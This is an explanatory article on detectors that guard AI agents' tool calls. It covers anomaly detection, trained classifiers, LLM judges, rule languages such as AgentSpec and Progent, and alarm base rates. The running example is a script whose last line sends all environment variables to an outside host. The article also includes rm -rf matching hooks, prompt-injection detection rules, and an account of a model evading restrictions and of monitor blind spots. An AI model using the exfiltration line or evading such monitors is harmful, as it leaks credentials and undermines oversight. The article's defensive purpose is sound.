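# Detectors for AI agent guardrails: behaviour, specification and code checks, and how they are combined

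## What a detector decides and what it compares an action with

An AI agent is a language model that works on a task by calling tools, for example to run shell commands, edit files, query databases or send messages. It can do damage if it misjudges the task or reads a page in which someone has hidden instructions for it, an attack called prompt injection. Developers therefore place a guardrail between the agent and its tools. The guardrail checks each action and allows it, blocks it or escalates it, usually to a person. It bases its decision on detectors, which are components that take an input, such as the proposed command or the record of the run so far, and return an alarm, a score or a verdict.

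The most useful question to ask about a detector for agents is what it compares an action with. This may be a learned model of bad or unusual conduct, a set of written rules, the meaning of a program's code, or a stated intention.

### The moment before a tool call runs

A model produces text and cannot run anything by itself, so a program around it, called the harness, runs the tools. OpenAI's *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (2026) describes the harness for Codex, the company's coding agent. The harness puts the user's request into a prompt and queries the model. The model either answers or requests a tool call, giving the tool's name and arguments. OpenAI's example is a request to run `ls`, which lists files, and report the output. The harness executes the call, appends the result to the prompt and queries the model again, until the model writes a message to the user instead of another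 call. The sequence of messages, calls and results is the run's trajectory.

A guardrail meant to prevent harm has to act after the agent requests a call and before the call is executed, while the call is only text and has changed nothing. Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, lets users intervene at this point with a hook, a script of their own that the harness runs after the model has filled in the call's arguments and before the harness processes the call. In an example from Anthropic's documentation, the hook searches shell commands for `rm -rf`, which deletes a directory and everything in it. When the agent proposes `rm -rf /tmp/build`, the hook returns "deny", the harness drops the call, and, according to Anthropic, the agent carries on.

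That teaching example is a complete guardrail with one detector, and it makes both kinds of error. It blocks the deletion of `/tmp/build`, which is probably scratch space that nobody needs. It also allows `rm -r -f`, which does the same thing as the blocked command but does not contain the string that the detector matches.

Many detectors in the research literature read recorded runs, and for those, when the alarm fires matters as much as whether it fires. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) replayed 1,931 successful attacks from AgentDojo, a benchmark in which planted instructions try to redirect tool-using agents. Its formal rules fired before the final harmful call in 52.4% of the attacks, only at that call in 17.7%, and never in 29.9%. An alarm at the final call counts as prevention if the guardrail holds each call until the check has finished, but it comes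 too late if the detector reads logs afterwards.

### Verdicts and errors

The possible verdicts differ slightly between papers. *What Can Be Enforced?* (2026) describes guardrails as monitors that block, rewrite or escalate a proposed action before it executes. *AgentTrust* (Yang, 2026), a guardrail for shell commands, cloud operations and other tool calls, uses allow, warn, block and escalate. Often the detector returns only a number, and the guardrail's developer picks a threshold above which that number counts as an alarm. Lowering the threshold catches more harmful actions but also stops more harmless ones.

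A detector's false-positive rate is the share of harmless actions it blocks, and its miss rate, or false-negative rate, is the share of harmful actions it lets through. On a set of 630 actions, Yang measured a false-positive rate of 2.1% and a miss rate of 6.1% for written rules alone. Yang also tested the rules with an LLM judge, a language model prompted to give a verdict on another model's action, which intervened only when confident. Adding the judge reduced the miss rate to 0.9% and left the false-positive rate unchanged. Yang both built and tested the system, and the actions came from curated collections, so the comparison between the two set-ups is more trustworthy than the absolute figures.

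Reported rates also depend on whether they count whole runs or single actions. *Agent-Sentry* (2026) counts whole runs. It treats a harmless run as a success if the guardrail allows it, and an attack as blocked if the guardrail stops it at or before the injected action. Other papers count single actions, which can make the same guardrail look much better. If a detector wrongly blocks 1% of harmless calls and its errors are independent, it will block at least one call in about 40% of harmless runs with fifty calls.

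### One script, four comparisons

Suppose a user asks an agent to post a summary of last night's failed builds in the team channel. (A build is an automated run that compiles and tests software.) The agent proposes a single tool call, which is to run this Python script:

```python
import os, requests

builds = requests.get(BUILD_SERVER, params={"status": "failed"}).json()
lines = [f"{b['name']}: {b['error']}" for b in builds]
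requests.post(TEAM_CHANNEL, json={"text": "\n".join(lines)})
requests.post(METRICS_HOST, json=dict(os.environ))
```

Every line except the last does what the task requires. The last line sends all of the machine's environment variables, where developers commonly keep passwords and access keys, to `METRICS_HOST`, an address outside the company. The call looks the same whether somebody hid an instruction in a build log or the model reproduced a snippet from its training data.

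- A behaviour detector judges the action by a learned or model-made notion of harmful or unusual conduct, and could raise an alarm because posting every environment variable off-site resembles credential theft, or because this agent's earlier build summaries never contacted that address.
- A specification-based detector checks the action against explicit rules, and would find that `METRICS_HOST` is missing from the list of addresses that scripts may contact.
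- A code detector analyses the program, and would trace data from `os.environ` into an outgoing network request.
- An intent comparison sets the action beside what the user, the agent or a tool's description said would happen, and would find that a request about failed builds gives no reason to send environment variables anywhere.

All four can catch this script, for different reasons, but they can disagree after small changes to it. If the last line sent only a count of failed builds to the company's own monitoring service, the script would be ordinary telemetry, though its text would hardly change. Yang uses such pairs to argue that patterns can detect threats with a fixed signature, such as `rm -rf /`, but that when a threat depends on destination, content or scope, any rule strict enough to block the attack also blocks the harmless version. His evidence is that adding a pack of cloud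 rules raised accuracy on unseen cases from 48% to 56% but did not change it in the categories for databases, monitoring and software dependencies. This is good evidence about patterns matched against command text but weaker evidence about rules in general, because a list of permitted destinations does distinguish the two versions of the script, at least until an attacker finds a way to send data through a permitted destination.

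The script also shows that one tool call can contain several actions. Once the script is running, its network requests do not go back through the harness for approval. *guardscope* (Toyoda, Leung and Bhuvaneswari, 2026) tested real runtime controls with a fixed set of actions and compared the controls' records with activity observed in the operating system's kernel. No control inside the harness checked direct network connections. A guardrail in that position can judge only the script's text, and only once, before the script runs.

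### The ancestry in intrusion detection

Comparing conduct with a norm is an old idea in computer security. Axelsson (1999), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, cites a 1980 report by James P. Anderson, who wanted to find people using somebody else's identity by searching audit logs for use at odd hours or in abnormal volume. Dorothy Denning's 1987 intrusion-detection model developed this into anomaly detection, in which a system keeps a statistical profile of each user's normal activity and flags departures from it. In the rival method, signature matching, the defender decides in advance what is undesirable, writes down the signs of such attacks and searches for them.

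Axelsson's journal article *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000) explains that anomaly detection is meant to catch novel attacks and abuses of legitimate privileges, but that an attacker may gradually train the system to treat his activities as normal. Signatures catch known attacks quickly but have difficulty with unknown ones.

Specification-based detection was a response to the second problem. *Specification-based Detection for Unix Privileged Programs* (Ko, 1995) addresses programs that run with an administrator's rights and contain subtle vulnerabilities. Signatures help only after somebody has found the vulnerability. Ko instead specified what each program was supposed to do and had a monitor report any other behaviour. In tests with several known attacks, the prototype detected them immediately. Ko, Manfred Ruschitzka and Karl Levitt published a full-length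 account of the approach in 1997.

The categories for agents correspond only loosely to the earlier intrusion-detection categories. Specification-based detectors for agents include lists of forbidden things as well as lists of permitted ones, so they include the hook that searches for `rm -rf`, which Axelsson would have called a signature. Behaviour detectors differ more from their predecessors. Denning's profiles came from the subject's own past, whereas an LLM judge applies a general notion of harm learned in training and needs no history of the agent. *TraceAegis* (2025) is closer to Denning's approach, since it learns from normal runs and looks for tool calls that break the expected order of a workflow or do not fit together in meaning, but it expresses the learned norm as rules and checks new runs against them.

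Code detectors and intent comparison have no real counterpart in the old pair. The monitors of the 1990s watched programs that an administrator had installed, whereas an agent writes a new program for each task, and the harness has the program's text before it runs. Audit logs also did not record what the user wanted, while an agent's run usually opens with the user's request. *Intent-Aware Protection for AI Agents* (2026) separately tests whether an explicit representation of the agent's intent helps detectors before and after execution.

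This division is not standard. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026), a survey, sorts guardrails by whether they check the agent's inputs or outputs and by whether they use rules or a model. It lists agreement with the user's intent as one of several output checks. The categories in the two schemes don't match one to one, because the same LLM judge can apply a general sense of harm, a written policy or the user's request, depending on its prompt. Products also mix the kinds of detector. LlamaFirewall, for example, combines a jailbreak detector, a check against the agent's stated goal and a code scanner.

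### How many alarms are right

Neither error rate tells the person who receives an alarm how likely it is to be right. That also depends on the base rate, the share of all actions that are harmful. With base rate *b*, miss rate *m* and false-positive rate *f*,

$$\text{share of alarms that are right} = \frac{b\,(1-m)}{b\,(1-m) + (1-b)\,f}$$

In an invented example, an agent makes 100,000 tool calls, of which 100 are harmful, so *b* is 0.1%. The detector has a miss rate of 10% and a false-positive rate of 1%. It raises 90 alarms on the harmful calls and 999 on the 99,900 harmless ones, so 90 of 1,089 alarms are right, about 8%. Removing every miss would raise that share only to 9%, while cutting the false-positive rate to 0.1% would raise it to 47%. When the detector raises no alarm, it is nearly always right, mostly because harmful calls are rare to begin with. Only 10 of the 98,911 calls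 that pass are harmful, but one of those 10 may be the script above.

Axelsson made this argument by imagining a small installation that produces a million audit records a day, with two intrusions that affect ten records each. Even if a detector misses nothing, its false-positive rate has to be about 1 in 100,000 for two-thirds of its alarms to be right; at a rate of 1 in 1,000, about 2% are right. He made clear that the record and intrusion frequencies were assumptions. He also drew on studies of plant control rooms, which suggested that most operators stop trusting a device well before half its alarms are false. For a guardrail, the share of correct alarms can be lower if an alarm only sends the call to a slower, more careful check, but it needs to be higher if each alarm stops the work.

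Work on agents has begun to report the share of alarms that are correct. *StepShield* (2026) calculated it for a test set in which 8.1% of cases were rogue. An LLM judge that missed 4.6% of rogue cases and flagged 5.6% of harmless ones was right in about 60% of its alarms. A pattern-based guard that flagged 78% of harmless cases was right in 9% of its alarms. The paper calls the 8.1% base rate realistic, which is doubtful for most deployments. If one case in a thousand were rogue, the same judge would be right in about one of every sixty alarms.

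Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026) audited eleven evaluations in *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*. Attacks or anomalies made up between 16% and 86% of the test samples, and none of the evaluations varied that share. They then trained a simple detector on which tools a run called and on general features such as its length. Its AUROC, the probability that it scores a random attack above a random harmless run, was 0.879, but when 2% of runs were attacks, it raised 12.2 false alarms for every true one. At that same attack rate, the share of alarms that were correct ranged from 3.9% to 11.7%, depending on how many of the harmless runs resembled attacks. A team whose agents routinely send telemetry to outside services can therefore expect a different figure from the one in the benchmark.

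## Behaviour detectors: learned judgements of what an agent does

Developers build behaviour detectors in three main ways. An anomaly detector learns from normal runs and scores departures from them, a trained classifier learns from runs labelled safe or unsafe, and an LLM judge gets a policy in its prompt and needs no further training.

### Anomaly detection: learning what is normal

Forrest, Hofmeyr and colleagues (1996), in *A Sense of Self for Unix Processes*, monitored system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system, for instance to open a file. They defined a program's normal behaviour by which calls tend to occur close together. Suppose a program normally calls open, read, write and close, in that order, and the detector records which calls come one or two places after each call. This gives five pairs. If the program later calls open, read, `execve` and close, where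 `execve` starts another program, three of the five pairs are new. The detector raises an alarm when it finds enough new pairs. In the first experiments, the definition of normal stayed stable for standard Unix programs, and the method detected several common intrusions through the mail program sendmail and the printing program lpr.

The detector first needs a record of normal behaviour. Hofmeyr, Forrest and Somayaji (1998), in *Intrusion Detection using Sequences of System Calls*, collected this both by running a program in as many ordinary ways as possible and by tracing live use. Deliberate runs can miss legitimate uses, which then cause false alarms, and live traces can contain an unnoticed attack. Later researchers criticised the method mainly for its false alarms and its weakness against mimicry, in which an attacker arranges harmful calls to resemble a normal sequence.

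Advani (2026), in *Trajectory Guard*, applies the idea to agents. The input is the user's task and the agent's steps, each turned into an embedding, a list of numbers that represents its meaning. One small network maps the task to a vector. A recurrent network reads the steps in order and compresses them into a second vector of 128 numbers, from which a decoder tries to rebuild the sequence. Training minimises

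$$L = L_{\text{match}} + 0.5\,L_{\text{rebuild}}$$

The first term pulls a task towards its own steps and away from the steps of other runs, so steps that don't suit the task should lie far from it. The second term penalises errors in the rebuilt sequence, so steps in an unusual order should be hard to rebuild.

The detector trained on 5,752 normal runs of business tasks, such as banking and telecoms, and harmless tool use from a safety dataset. For the main test, GPT-5 inserted one to three invalid steps into unseen runs. The detector caught 91% of these anomalies, and 94% of its alarms were correct. The test had 836 anomalies and 1,000 normal runs, so the false-positive rate was about 5%. At that rate, if one run in a thousand were anomalous, fewer than one alarm in fifty would be correct.

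The order of the steps matters a lot. Standard anomaly detectors that averaged the embeddings of all steps had F1 scores of at most 0.69, because averaging hides a single bad step. F1 combines precision, the share of alarms that are right, and recall, the share of anomalies caught. Trajectory Guard, a small detector, scored 0.92. The best of four LLM judges scored 0.95 but took about 600 milliseconds per run, compared with 32 for Trajectory Guard on a graphics processor. Trajectory Guard did worse on long runs, scoring 0.87 on those of eleven or more steps and 0.96 on those of two to five.

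Advani also reports that the detector caught 86% of 3,802 anomalous runs from a security benchmark and 92% of 184 failure logs from multi-agent systems. These results are weaker evidence than they look, because neither collection included normal runs and a detector that flagged everything would have scored 100%. The detector may also have flagged some cases because their format was unfamiliar.

### Classifiers trained on labelled runs

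A detector trained on both normal and intrusive runs can learn the difference directly. *Learning Patterns from Unix Process Execution Traces for Intrusion Detection* (1997) extended Forrest's work in this direction. Its classifiers, trained on both kinds of sendmail run, separated all the intrusive test runs from the normal ones.

For agents, it is hard to get enough labelled runs. *AgentDoG* (2026), from the Shanghai Artificial Intelligence Laboratory, generates synthetic ones. A planning model selects where a risk comes from, how the agent fails and what harm follows (for example, a corrupted tool result, an action without the user's consent and a financial loss). It also selects whether the agent will handle the risk safely. Other model components then write the user's request, the tool results and the agent's responses. The pipeline generated more than 100,000 runs with about 10,000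 tools, and automatic checks kept roughly 52% of its output.

The laboratory used these runs to fine-tune language models of 4 to 8 billion parameters. The classifier's input is a whole trajectory, and it labels the run unsafe if at least one step is unsafe:

$$y = \text{unsafe} \iff \exists i:\ \text{Unsafe}(t_i)$$

where each step *t<sub>i</sub>* is an action together with the observation that follows it. Separately trained versions name the source of the risk, the type of failure and the harm. An agent that meets a hidden instruction and ignores it counts as safe.

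On ATBench, the laboratory's own test set of 500 runs, the 4-billion-parameter version missed 4.4% of unsafe runs and flagged about 10% of safe ones. Llama Guard 4, a model built to moderate conversations, missed 84% of the unsafe runs. The test used tools that were absent from training, but the same pipeline generated the training and test runs. *AgentDoG 1.5* (2026) tested the earlier model on a new ATBench of 1,000 runs, where it missed 11% of the unsafe runs and flagged about 61% of the safe ones. The new set is harder in general, since GPT-5.2's accuracy also fell, from 90% to 69%. Even so, 61% is too many false alarms for the model to be used as an automatic block.

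The newer version needs far less training data. The laboratory scored each candidate example by whether learning from it would push the model towards recognising risks, and kept about 1,000. GPT-5.4 wrote a step-by-step rationale for each of these. The resulting 4-billion-parameter model missed 20% of unsafe runs in the new ATBench and flagged 35% of safe ones. It missed more unsafe runs than the earlier version but raised fewer false alarms, and its accuracy rose from 64% to 72%.

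The explanations are less reliable than the verdicts. The model that *AgentDoG 1.5* trained specifically for diagnosis identified the right risk source in 75% of unsafe runs, but the right type of failure in only 28%. Someone investigating an alarm can use these labels as a hint about where to look, but they are too unreliable to treat as findings.

Mou, Xue and colleagues (2026), in *ToolSafe*, trained TS-Guard, a classifier that checks single tool calls before they run. It receives the user's request, the history so far and the agent's proposed call. It writes a short analysis, then judges whether the request is harmful, whether the call is linked to an attack, and whether the call is safe, controversial or unsafe. Training used reinforcement learning on only 2,193 labelled steps, with a reward of 1 for three correct judgements and a deduction of one third for each mistake.

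Mou and colleagues counted controversial steps as unsafe in their main results, and the false-positive rates implied by those results vary widely between test sets. TS-Guard flagged about 4% of safe steps on a set that came from the same benchmark as much of its training data, but from other domains. It flagged about 7% on AgentDojo, the prompt-injection benchmark, and about 46% on AgentHarm, which contains harmful requests. Accuracy on AgentHarm was still 85% because most steps there were unsafe and TS-Guard caught 97% of those. Even 7% is high for a check that runs before every call. If the errors were independent, about half of harmless runs with ten calls would have at least one false alarm.

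*StepGuard* (2026) addresses this imbalance. It fine-tunes a 4-billion-parameter model on 3,000 generated examples, then adds a round of reinforcement learning to narrow the gap between the model's performance on safe and unsafe actions. The model can check either a full run or a single proposed call.

### LLM judges with a policy in the prompt

A developer can also prompt a general-purpose language model instead of training a detector. The prompt contains a policy, the tool descriptions, the action or trajectory and the required output format, and the model generates some reasoning and a verdict. For the script in the previous section, the policy might be "do not send credentials outside the company". The model would still have to recognise that environment variables often contain credentials and that `METRICS_HOST` is outside the company. This design therefore combines two kinds of detector,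 since the policy is a written specification but deciding whether an action falls under it takes learned judgement.

The main advantage of this type of classifier is that the developer can change the norm by editing a paragraph. Claude Code's auto mode and LlamaFirewall's AlignmentCheck both use one, although AlignmentCheck compares the agent's reasoning with the user's goal.

Prompted judges have the same trouble with harmless runs as trained classifiers. The rates below are calculated from the precision and recall that *AgentDoG 1.5* reports on the new ATBench. The unified variant is a version of the 4-billion-parameter model trained on the verdict and the diagnosis together.

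| Detector | Unsafe runs missed | Safe runs flagged |
|---|---:|---:|
| GPT-5.4, prompted | 13% | 40% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro, prompted | 26% | 23% |
| AgentDoG 1.0, 4 billion parameters | 11% | 61% |
| AgentDoG 1.5, 4 billion parameters | 20% | 35% |
| AgentDoG 1.5, unified variant | 24% | 19% |

The small unified model did about as well as Gemini 3.1 Pro, which could make it cheaper to check every run. But the laboratory that trained it also built the test, which pairs risky situations that an agent handled well with ones it handled badly. Ordinary harmless work should be easier to recognise. The table is therefore best read as a measure of how well the detectors handle difficult cases, not as a prediction of how often they would interrupt a team's daily work.

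### Predicting an unsafe state before it arrives

*ProbGuard* (Wang, Poskitt and colleagues, 2025) is designed to estimate what an agent will do later. *Sovereign Agentic Loops* (He and Yu, 2026) describes the system, under its earlier name Pro2Guard, as a move from reactive to proactive enforcement. The motivating example is a household robot that turns on the stove and then leaves the kitchen to fetch a parcel. If the rule is that the stove may not be unattended for more than ten minutes, a detector that waits for a violation will fire only after the ten minutes have passed.

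ProbGuard starts with true-or-false statements chosen by an expert, such as "the stove is on" and "the agent is in the kitchen". Each valid combination of true and false values is a state, and the expert marks the unsafe ones. The system then counts transitions between states in recorded runs. For example, 31 of 184 transitions from "stove off, agent in the kitchen" led to a state with the stove on, so the estimated probability of that transition is 16.85%. These probabilities form a Markov chain, a model in which the probability of the next state depends only on the current one. During a run, the monitor looks up the current state, computes the probability that the agent will never reach an unsafe state, and intervenes when this falls below a threshold.

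An invented chain with three states shows the calculation. In state *A* the stove is on and the agent is away. In state *S* the stove is off and the task is over. In state *U* the agent has been away too long. Of 200 recorded transitions from *A*, 140 stayed in *A*, 40 went to *S* and 20 went to *U*, which gives probabilities of 0.7, 0.2 and 0.1. Let *h* be the probability of ever reaching *U* from *A*. The agent either goes there at once or stays in *A* and faces the same risk again:

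$$h = 0.1 + 0.7h \quad\Rightarrow\quad h = \frac{0.1}{1-0.7} = \frac{1}{3}$$

The next step is 10% likely to be unsafe, but the agent has a 67% chance of staying safe throughout. With a threshold of 80%, the monitor would intervene as soon as the agent left the kitchen.

Rare events may not appear in the records. If the records had contained 60 transitions to *S* and none to *U*, the estimated risk would be zero. To avoid this, ProbGuard adds a small constant to the count of every transition that the expert considers possible. With a constant of 1, the counts become 141, 61 and 1, and *h* becomes 1/62, or about 1.6%. This estimate depends heavily on the constant because it isn't based on any observed transitions to *U*.

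The chain's prediction also depends only on its current state. In the invented example, this makes the risk the same after one minute away as after nine, which is wrong. An expert can fix this by splitting *A* by elapsed time, but each added yes-or-no statement can double the number of states and leaves fewer observations for each one.

Wang and colleagues tested the system on simulated driving and household tasks. It warned of traffic violations and collisions up to 15.84 seconds ahead at a threshold that produced no false alarms. For household agents, prompting the agent again after an alarm reduced unsafe behaviour by 65% and kept 80% of the original task completion. Halting the agent instead reduced unsafe behaviour by 94%, but the agent completed fewer tasks. In these settings, a few variables, such as speed or the state of a stove, capture most of the danger. It is much harder to see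 which twenty yes-or-no statements would capture most of the danger for an agent with a shell and internet access.

### Judging one action or the whole run

Detectors that check one action at a time can miss a series of steps that leads to a harmful result even though each step looks acceptable. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (20 July 2026) explains why the company added trajectory-level monitoring for an internal model that works on its own for long periods. During limited internal use, the model had sometimes persisted in getting around restrictions in ways that checks on individual actions did not stop. OpenAI paused access and built a monitor that follows the whole trajectory as it grows and looks for signs that the model is bypassing a user's constraint or a safety boundary. The monitor can pause the session and alert the user, who can let the work continue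 if the alarm was false.

OpenAI then replayed a small set of earlier situations in which the model had misbehaved. The new safeguards caught considerably more of the misaligned actions, and the company judged every remaining miss to be of low severity. It has seen no serious circumvention in the several weeks since it restored access. These results support trajectory monitoring only to a degree, because OpenAI gives no error rates and the model did not always repeat its earlier behaviour in the replays. The company had also retrained the model to remember instructions better over long runs, which may explain the lack of serious circumvention as much as the monitor does. The first version of the safeguards was deliberately conservative, and OpenAI has since been tuning it to reduce unnecessary interruptions.

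The two approaches overlap. TS-Guard judges a single call but reads the history first, while AgentDoG judges a whole run but its definition of an unsafe run requires at least one unsafe step. That definition covers the cases that worried OpenAI only if whether a step is "unsafe" can depend on everything that came before it. In practice, it matters more how much history the detector sees and whether its training or prompt directs it to look for harm that builds up over several steps.

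Detectors that read more of an agent's history need more computation. If an agent makes 50 calls and each adds 1,000 tokens (the units of text that a model processes), a detector that reads only the newest step processes 50,000 tokens in all. A detector that rereads the entire run before each call processes 1,000 × (1 + 2 + … + 50), or 1.275 million, unless it can reuse earlier computation. ProbGuard avoids this rereading by reducing the history to a state, and Trajectory Guard by reducing it to 128 numbers, but both lose detail.

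*AgentDoG 1.5* instead checks the run once, just before the agent sends its final reply. On 260 test cases in which an attacker tried to make the agent reveal hidden instructions and similar information, the 4-billion-parameter model reduced the share of harmful replies from 42% to 27%. Two conversational guard models did not reduce it. However, the test included only harm that blocking a reply could prevent. A check at this point is too late to prevent harm from the agent's earlier actions, such as deleting a database.

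### Unusual conduct, changing tasks and inconsistent verdicts

Anomaly detectors can raise false alarms because unusual conduct is often harmless. In one of Advani's anomalies, the agent looks up new music, closes the music app, fetches a rock chart and opens a podcast app. That may be an inefficient way to do the task, but it does no harm. Missing harmful conduct because it resembles normal conduct is more dangerous. If an agent uploads files to a storage service every day, uploading the wrong file will look normal.

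An anomaly score does not have to block a run by itself. A detector that takes 32 milliseconds can select unusual runs for a slower check. However, harmful runs that look ordinary never reach that check. Labels help more with these runs, because a classifier can learn that some ordinary-looking actions are harmful.

Labelled examples and general-purpose judges have a similar problem. Mou and colleagues found that many models flagged harmless calls just because a prompt injection appeared somewhere in the history. GPT-4o, a 2024 model, caught every unsafe step on AgentDojo but also flagged about 62% of the safe ones, apparently because an attack was present, even when the agent wasn't obeying it. TS-Guard is meant to prevent this by answering a separate question about whether the call is linked to the attack. Training it on all three questions produced fewer false positives than training on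 the safety verdict alone. On the same AgentDojo steps, it flagged about 7% of the safe ones and missed about 11% of the unsafe ones.

Normal conduct also changes with the task. Forrest's method could rely on sendmail doing much the same thing every day, whereas a general-purpose agent may repair a website in the morning and sort invoices in the afternoon. Advani therefore compares the steps with the task, so that the detector learns which steps suit which request. Training with the matching term alone gave an F1 score of 0.82 on validation runs, and adding the rebuilding term raised it to 0.92. But an earlier attempt that relied only on matching transferred badly between run formats, and Trajectory Guard's training covered only two sources.

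The other response is to retrain the detector for particular agents. *AgentDoG 1.5* adapted its classifier to the record formats of OpenAI's Codex and the general assistant OpenClaw, and reached 80% and 84% accuracy on their test sets. This works for a developer who knows which agents the detector will monitor. The jump in false positives between the two versions of ATBench suggests that a classifier can fail badly even when the new runs come from the same laboratory and were produced in much the same way. A team should therefore measure false positives on its own agents' harmless runs before it lets any of these detectors block an action. For an agent with one narrow workflow, the old approach of learning its normal behaviour is much more promising.

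The last difficulty is that an LLM judge can give different verdicts on the same input, because a language model usually picks each word at random according to the probabilities it computes. Good measurements of this are scarce for agent guardrails, but there is more evidence of disagreement between different judges. When four models labelled the 500 runs of the first ATBench for *AgentDoG*, they were unanimous on only 273. The verdict in a large share of difficult cases can therefore depend on which judge a developer chooses, though this result does not measure how often one judge would contradict itself.

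A developer can make a judge more consistent by having it always choose the most probable next word, as *AgentDoG 1.5* did in its test of final replies. Training also helps. Mou and colleagues measured how widely the models spread their probabilities over possible next words, and found that TS-Guard's became much more concentrated at the point where it gives its verdict, so repeated runs should agree more often. But consistency is easy to achieve and is weak evidence of accuracy, since a judge can wrongly block the same harmless command every time.

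## Specification-based detectors: checking actions against written rules

A specification-based detector normally gives the same verdict for the same input, and anyone can read the rule that triggered an alarm, but someone has to decide in advance what the agent may do. The simplest rules depend only on the proposed call, while others also depend on earlier events in the run.

### AgentSpec: a trigger, a check and a response

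Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AGENTSPEC*, introduced a small language for rules about agents. A rule's trigger is an event, such as the agent being about to run Python. Its check is a list of predicates, which are conditions that come out true or false. If all of them are true, the system carries out the rule's enforcement. A rule for the build-summary script could look like this:

```
rule @unlisted_destination
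trigger
    PythonREPL
check
    posts_to_unlisted_host
enforce
    stop
end
```

When the agent proposes the script, AgentSpec evaluates the predicate, finds that `METRICS_HOST` is not on the list of permitted addresses, and ends the run before any line executes, so the user doesn't get the summary either. The developer could instead write `user_inspection`, which lets the user decide whether to proceed, or `llm_self_examine`, which sends the violation to the agent's model so that it can plan a different action. A fourth option runs an action that the developer has prepared.

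Most of the difficulty is in writing the predicate. AgentSpec's language has no built-in check for unlisted hosts, so a developer has to write a Python function that takes the user's request and the trajectory and returns true or false. A function that searched this script for web addresses would find none, because the script refers to them by name. Wang and colleagues used a source-code check in a similar rule about untrusted websites, and acknowledge that tracing data flow would make it more accurate.

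The AgentSpec paper tests hand-written rules on RedCode-Exec, a set of prompts that ask a coding agent to do something risky, and reports that the rules stopped over 90% of unsafe executions. Across all categories, the agent tried to run Python 422 times and the rules flagged 333 of those programs, or 79%. The share rises to 91% without two categories in which the agent ran code but hadn't written the bug that the prompt asked for. In the category for side-channel vulnerabilities, where a program leaks secrets through something like its timing, the rules flagged only 3 of 25 programs. On inspection, the researchers judged 58 of the 333 flagged programs to be harmless. The test included no ordinary programming tasks, so it gives no false-positive rate for everyday work.

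A test with simulated household robots included safe tasks as well as hazardous ones. Without rules, the agent carried out up to 79% of the hazardous tasks in a category. With rules, it carried out none, and its completion rate on safe tasks fell from 58.6% to 54.3%. One rule, which lets the robot pour liquid only onto things listed as safe to get wet, covered 96 of the 250 hazardous cases. But Wang and colleagues wrote the rules from the dataset's descriptions of its risks. The perfect score on hazardous tasks therefore shows that the rule language can express such rules, but it is weaker evidence that a developer would think of the right ones beforehand.

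The checks take very little time compared with an LLM judge. Evaluating the predicates took 2.83 milliseconds on average for code, in runs that lasted 25.4 seconds, and 1.11 milliseconds for the robots, in runs that lasted 9.8 seconds. These figures exclude the time a user or model takes to respond after a rule fires.

### Progent: blocking whatever no rule allows

AgentSpec's rules describe what to stop, and a call that violates none of them goes ahead. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) instead blocks any call that matches no rule. Each Progent rule allows or forbids one tool under conditions on its arguments. A case the developer forgets therefore usually causes a miss in AgentSpec and a false alarm in Progent.

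Suppose the agent in the running example had separate tools for fetching builds and posting messages. In a simplified version of Progent's notation, its policy could be:

```
allow get_builds    when status == "failed"
allow post_message  when channel == "team-builds"
```

This is enough for the task, and it blocks messages to any other channel without needing a list of bad ones. Progent checks the rules that forbid a call before those that allow it. By default, a blocked call returns an error message that explains the reason and repeats the user's task, so the agent can continue its legitimate work.

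The policy is much less useful if the agent has a Python interpreter, because the whole script is a single text argument that Progent can compare only with fixed values and text patterns. Shi and colleagues chose to check tool calls because tool names and typed arguments have a clear structure, but this advantage largely disappears when one of the arguments is a program.

A fixed policy also doesn't suit tasks whose steps become clear only along the way. In Shi and colleagues' example, the user asks the agent to do whatever an email from Alice lists, and the email turns out to require Slack. Progent has a language model propose changes to the policy as the run proceeds, then compares the old and new versions with an SMT solver, a program that decides whether logical formulas can be true. If *A(P)* is the set of calls that policy *P* allows, a new policy *P′* takes effect automatically only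 if

$$A(P') \subseteq A(P)$$

A change that limits Slack messages to one recipient passes this test, but one that adds permission to email an outside address fails and needs approval. The set of permitted calls can therefore only shrink between approvals, even if a prompt injection manipulates the model's proposed changes.

On AgentDojo, 39.9% of attacks succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On ASB, another benchmark that includes prompt injection, the success rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Shi and colleagues report that the agents did their tasks about as well as before. In these tests a simulated user approved every expansion of the policy, so the solver's check could not have stopped anything. Most of the reduction on AgentDojo came from the initial policy, which alone lowered the rate to 2.5%. GPT-4o wrote that policy from the user's request before receiving any content that an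 attacker could control.

The solver's guarantee covers permissions, and its usefulness depends on the policy and the approver. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Progent needs correct and complete policies, which people find hard to write by hand. Approval may be manageable, since only 6% of policy updates on AgentDojo needed it. But approval cannot stop an attack that requires no additional permission. Shi and colleagues place such attacks outside Progent's scope, giving the example of an attacker who tricks an agent into favouring one product among several valid options.

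### Rules about what happened earlier

A rule about a single call can restrict an agent's emails to addresses inside the company. It cannot express that the agent may send email in general, but not after reading a suspicious message. Invariant Labs' *Advanced Guardrails*, the documentation for a rule language for agents, covers this case with a rule of the following form (here with different names and a shorter error message):

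```
raise "email after suspicious inbox" if:
    (mail: ToolOutput) -> (out: ToolCall)
    mail is tool:get_inbox
    out is tool:send_email
    prompt_injection(mail.content)
```

The arrow matches a tool result followed, at any later point, by a tool call. The next two lines require the result to come from the inbox and the call to send an email. The last line passes the text of the inbox to a detector for prompt injections. If the agent reads an inbox that the detector flags, checks a calendar and then tries to send an email, the rule fires on the email. It fires even if the email contains nothing from the inbox, because the arrow checks the order of events and does not trace the data.

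`prompt_injection` is a trained classifier, so this written rule contains a learned judgement. The rule misses every attack that the classifier misses, and Invariant Labs warns that such classifiers are only a heuristic. But because the classifier is inside a rule, a false alarm about an inbox does no harm unless the agent later tries to send an email. Another Invariant Labs example reduces false alarms further by firing only when the recipient is outside the user's company.

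A developer could also delete the rule's last line. The rule would then need no classifier, and no injection could evade it by appearing harmless, but it would block the agent from ever replying to an email it had read.

### Which properties a monitor can enforce

All of these systems are monitors in a sense that computer scientists defined long before there were LLM agents. Let *τ* be the trajectory so far, *a* the action that the agent proposes, and *G* the set of trajectories that do not violate the property. Writing *τa* for the trajectory extended by *a*, the monitor follows the rule

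$$\text{block } a \iff \tau a \notin G$$

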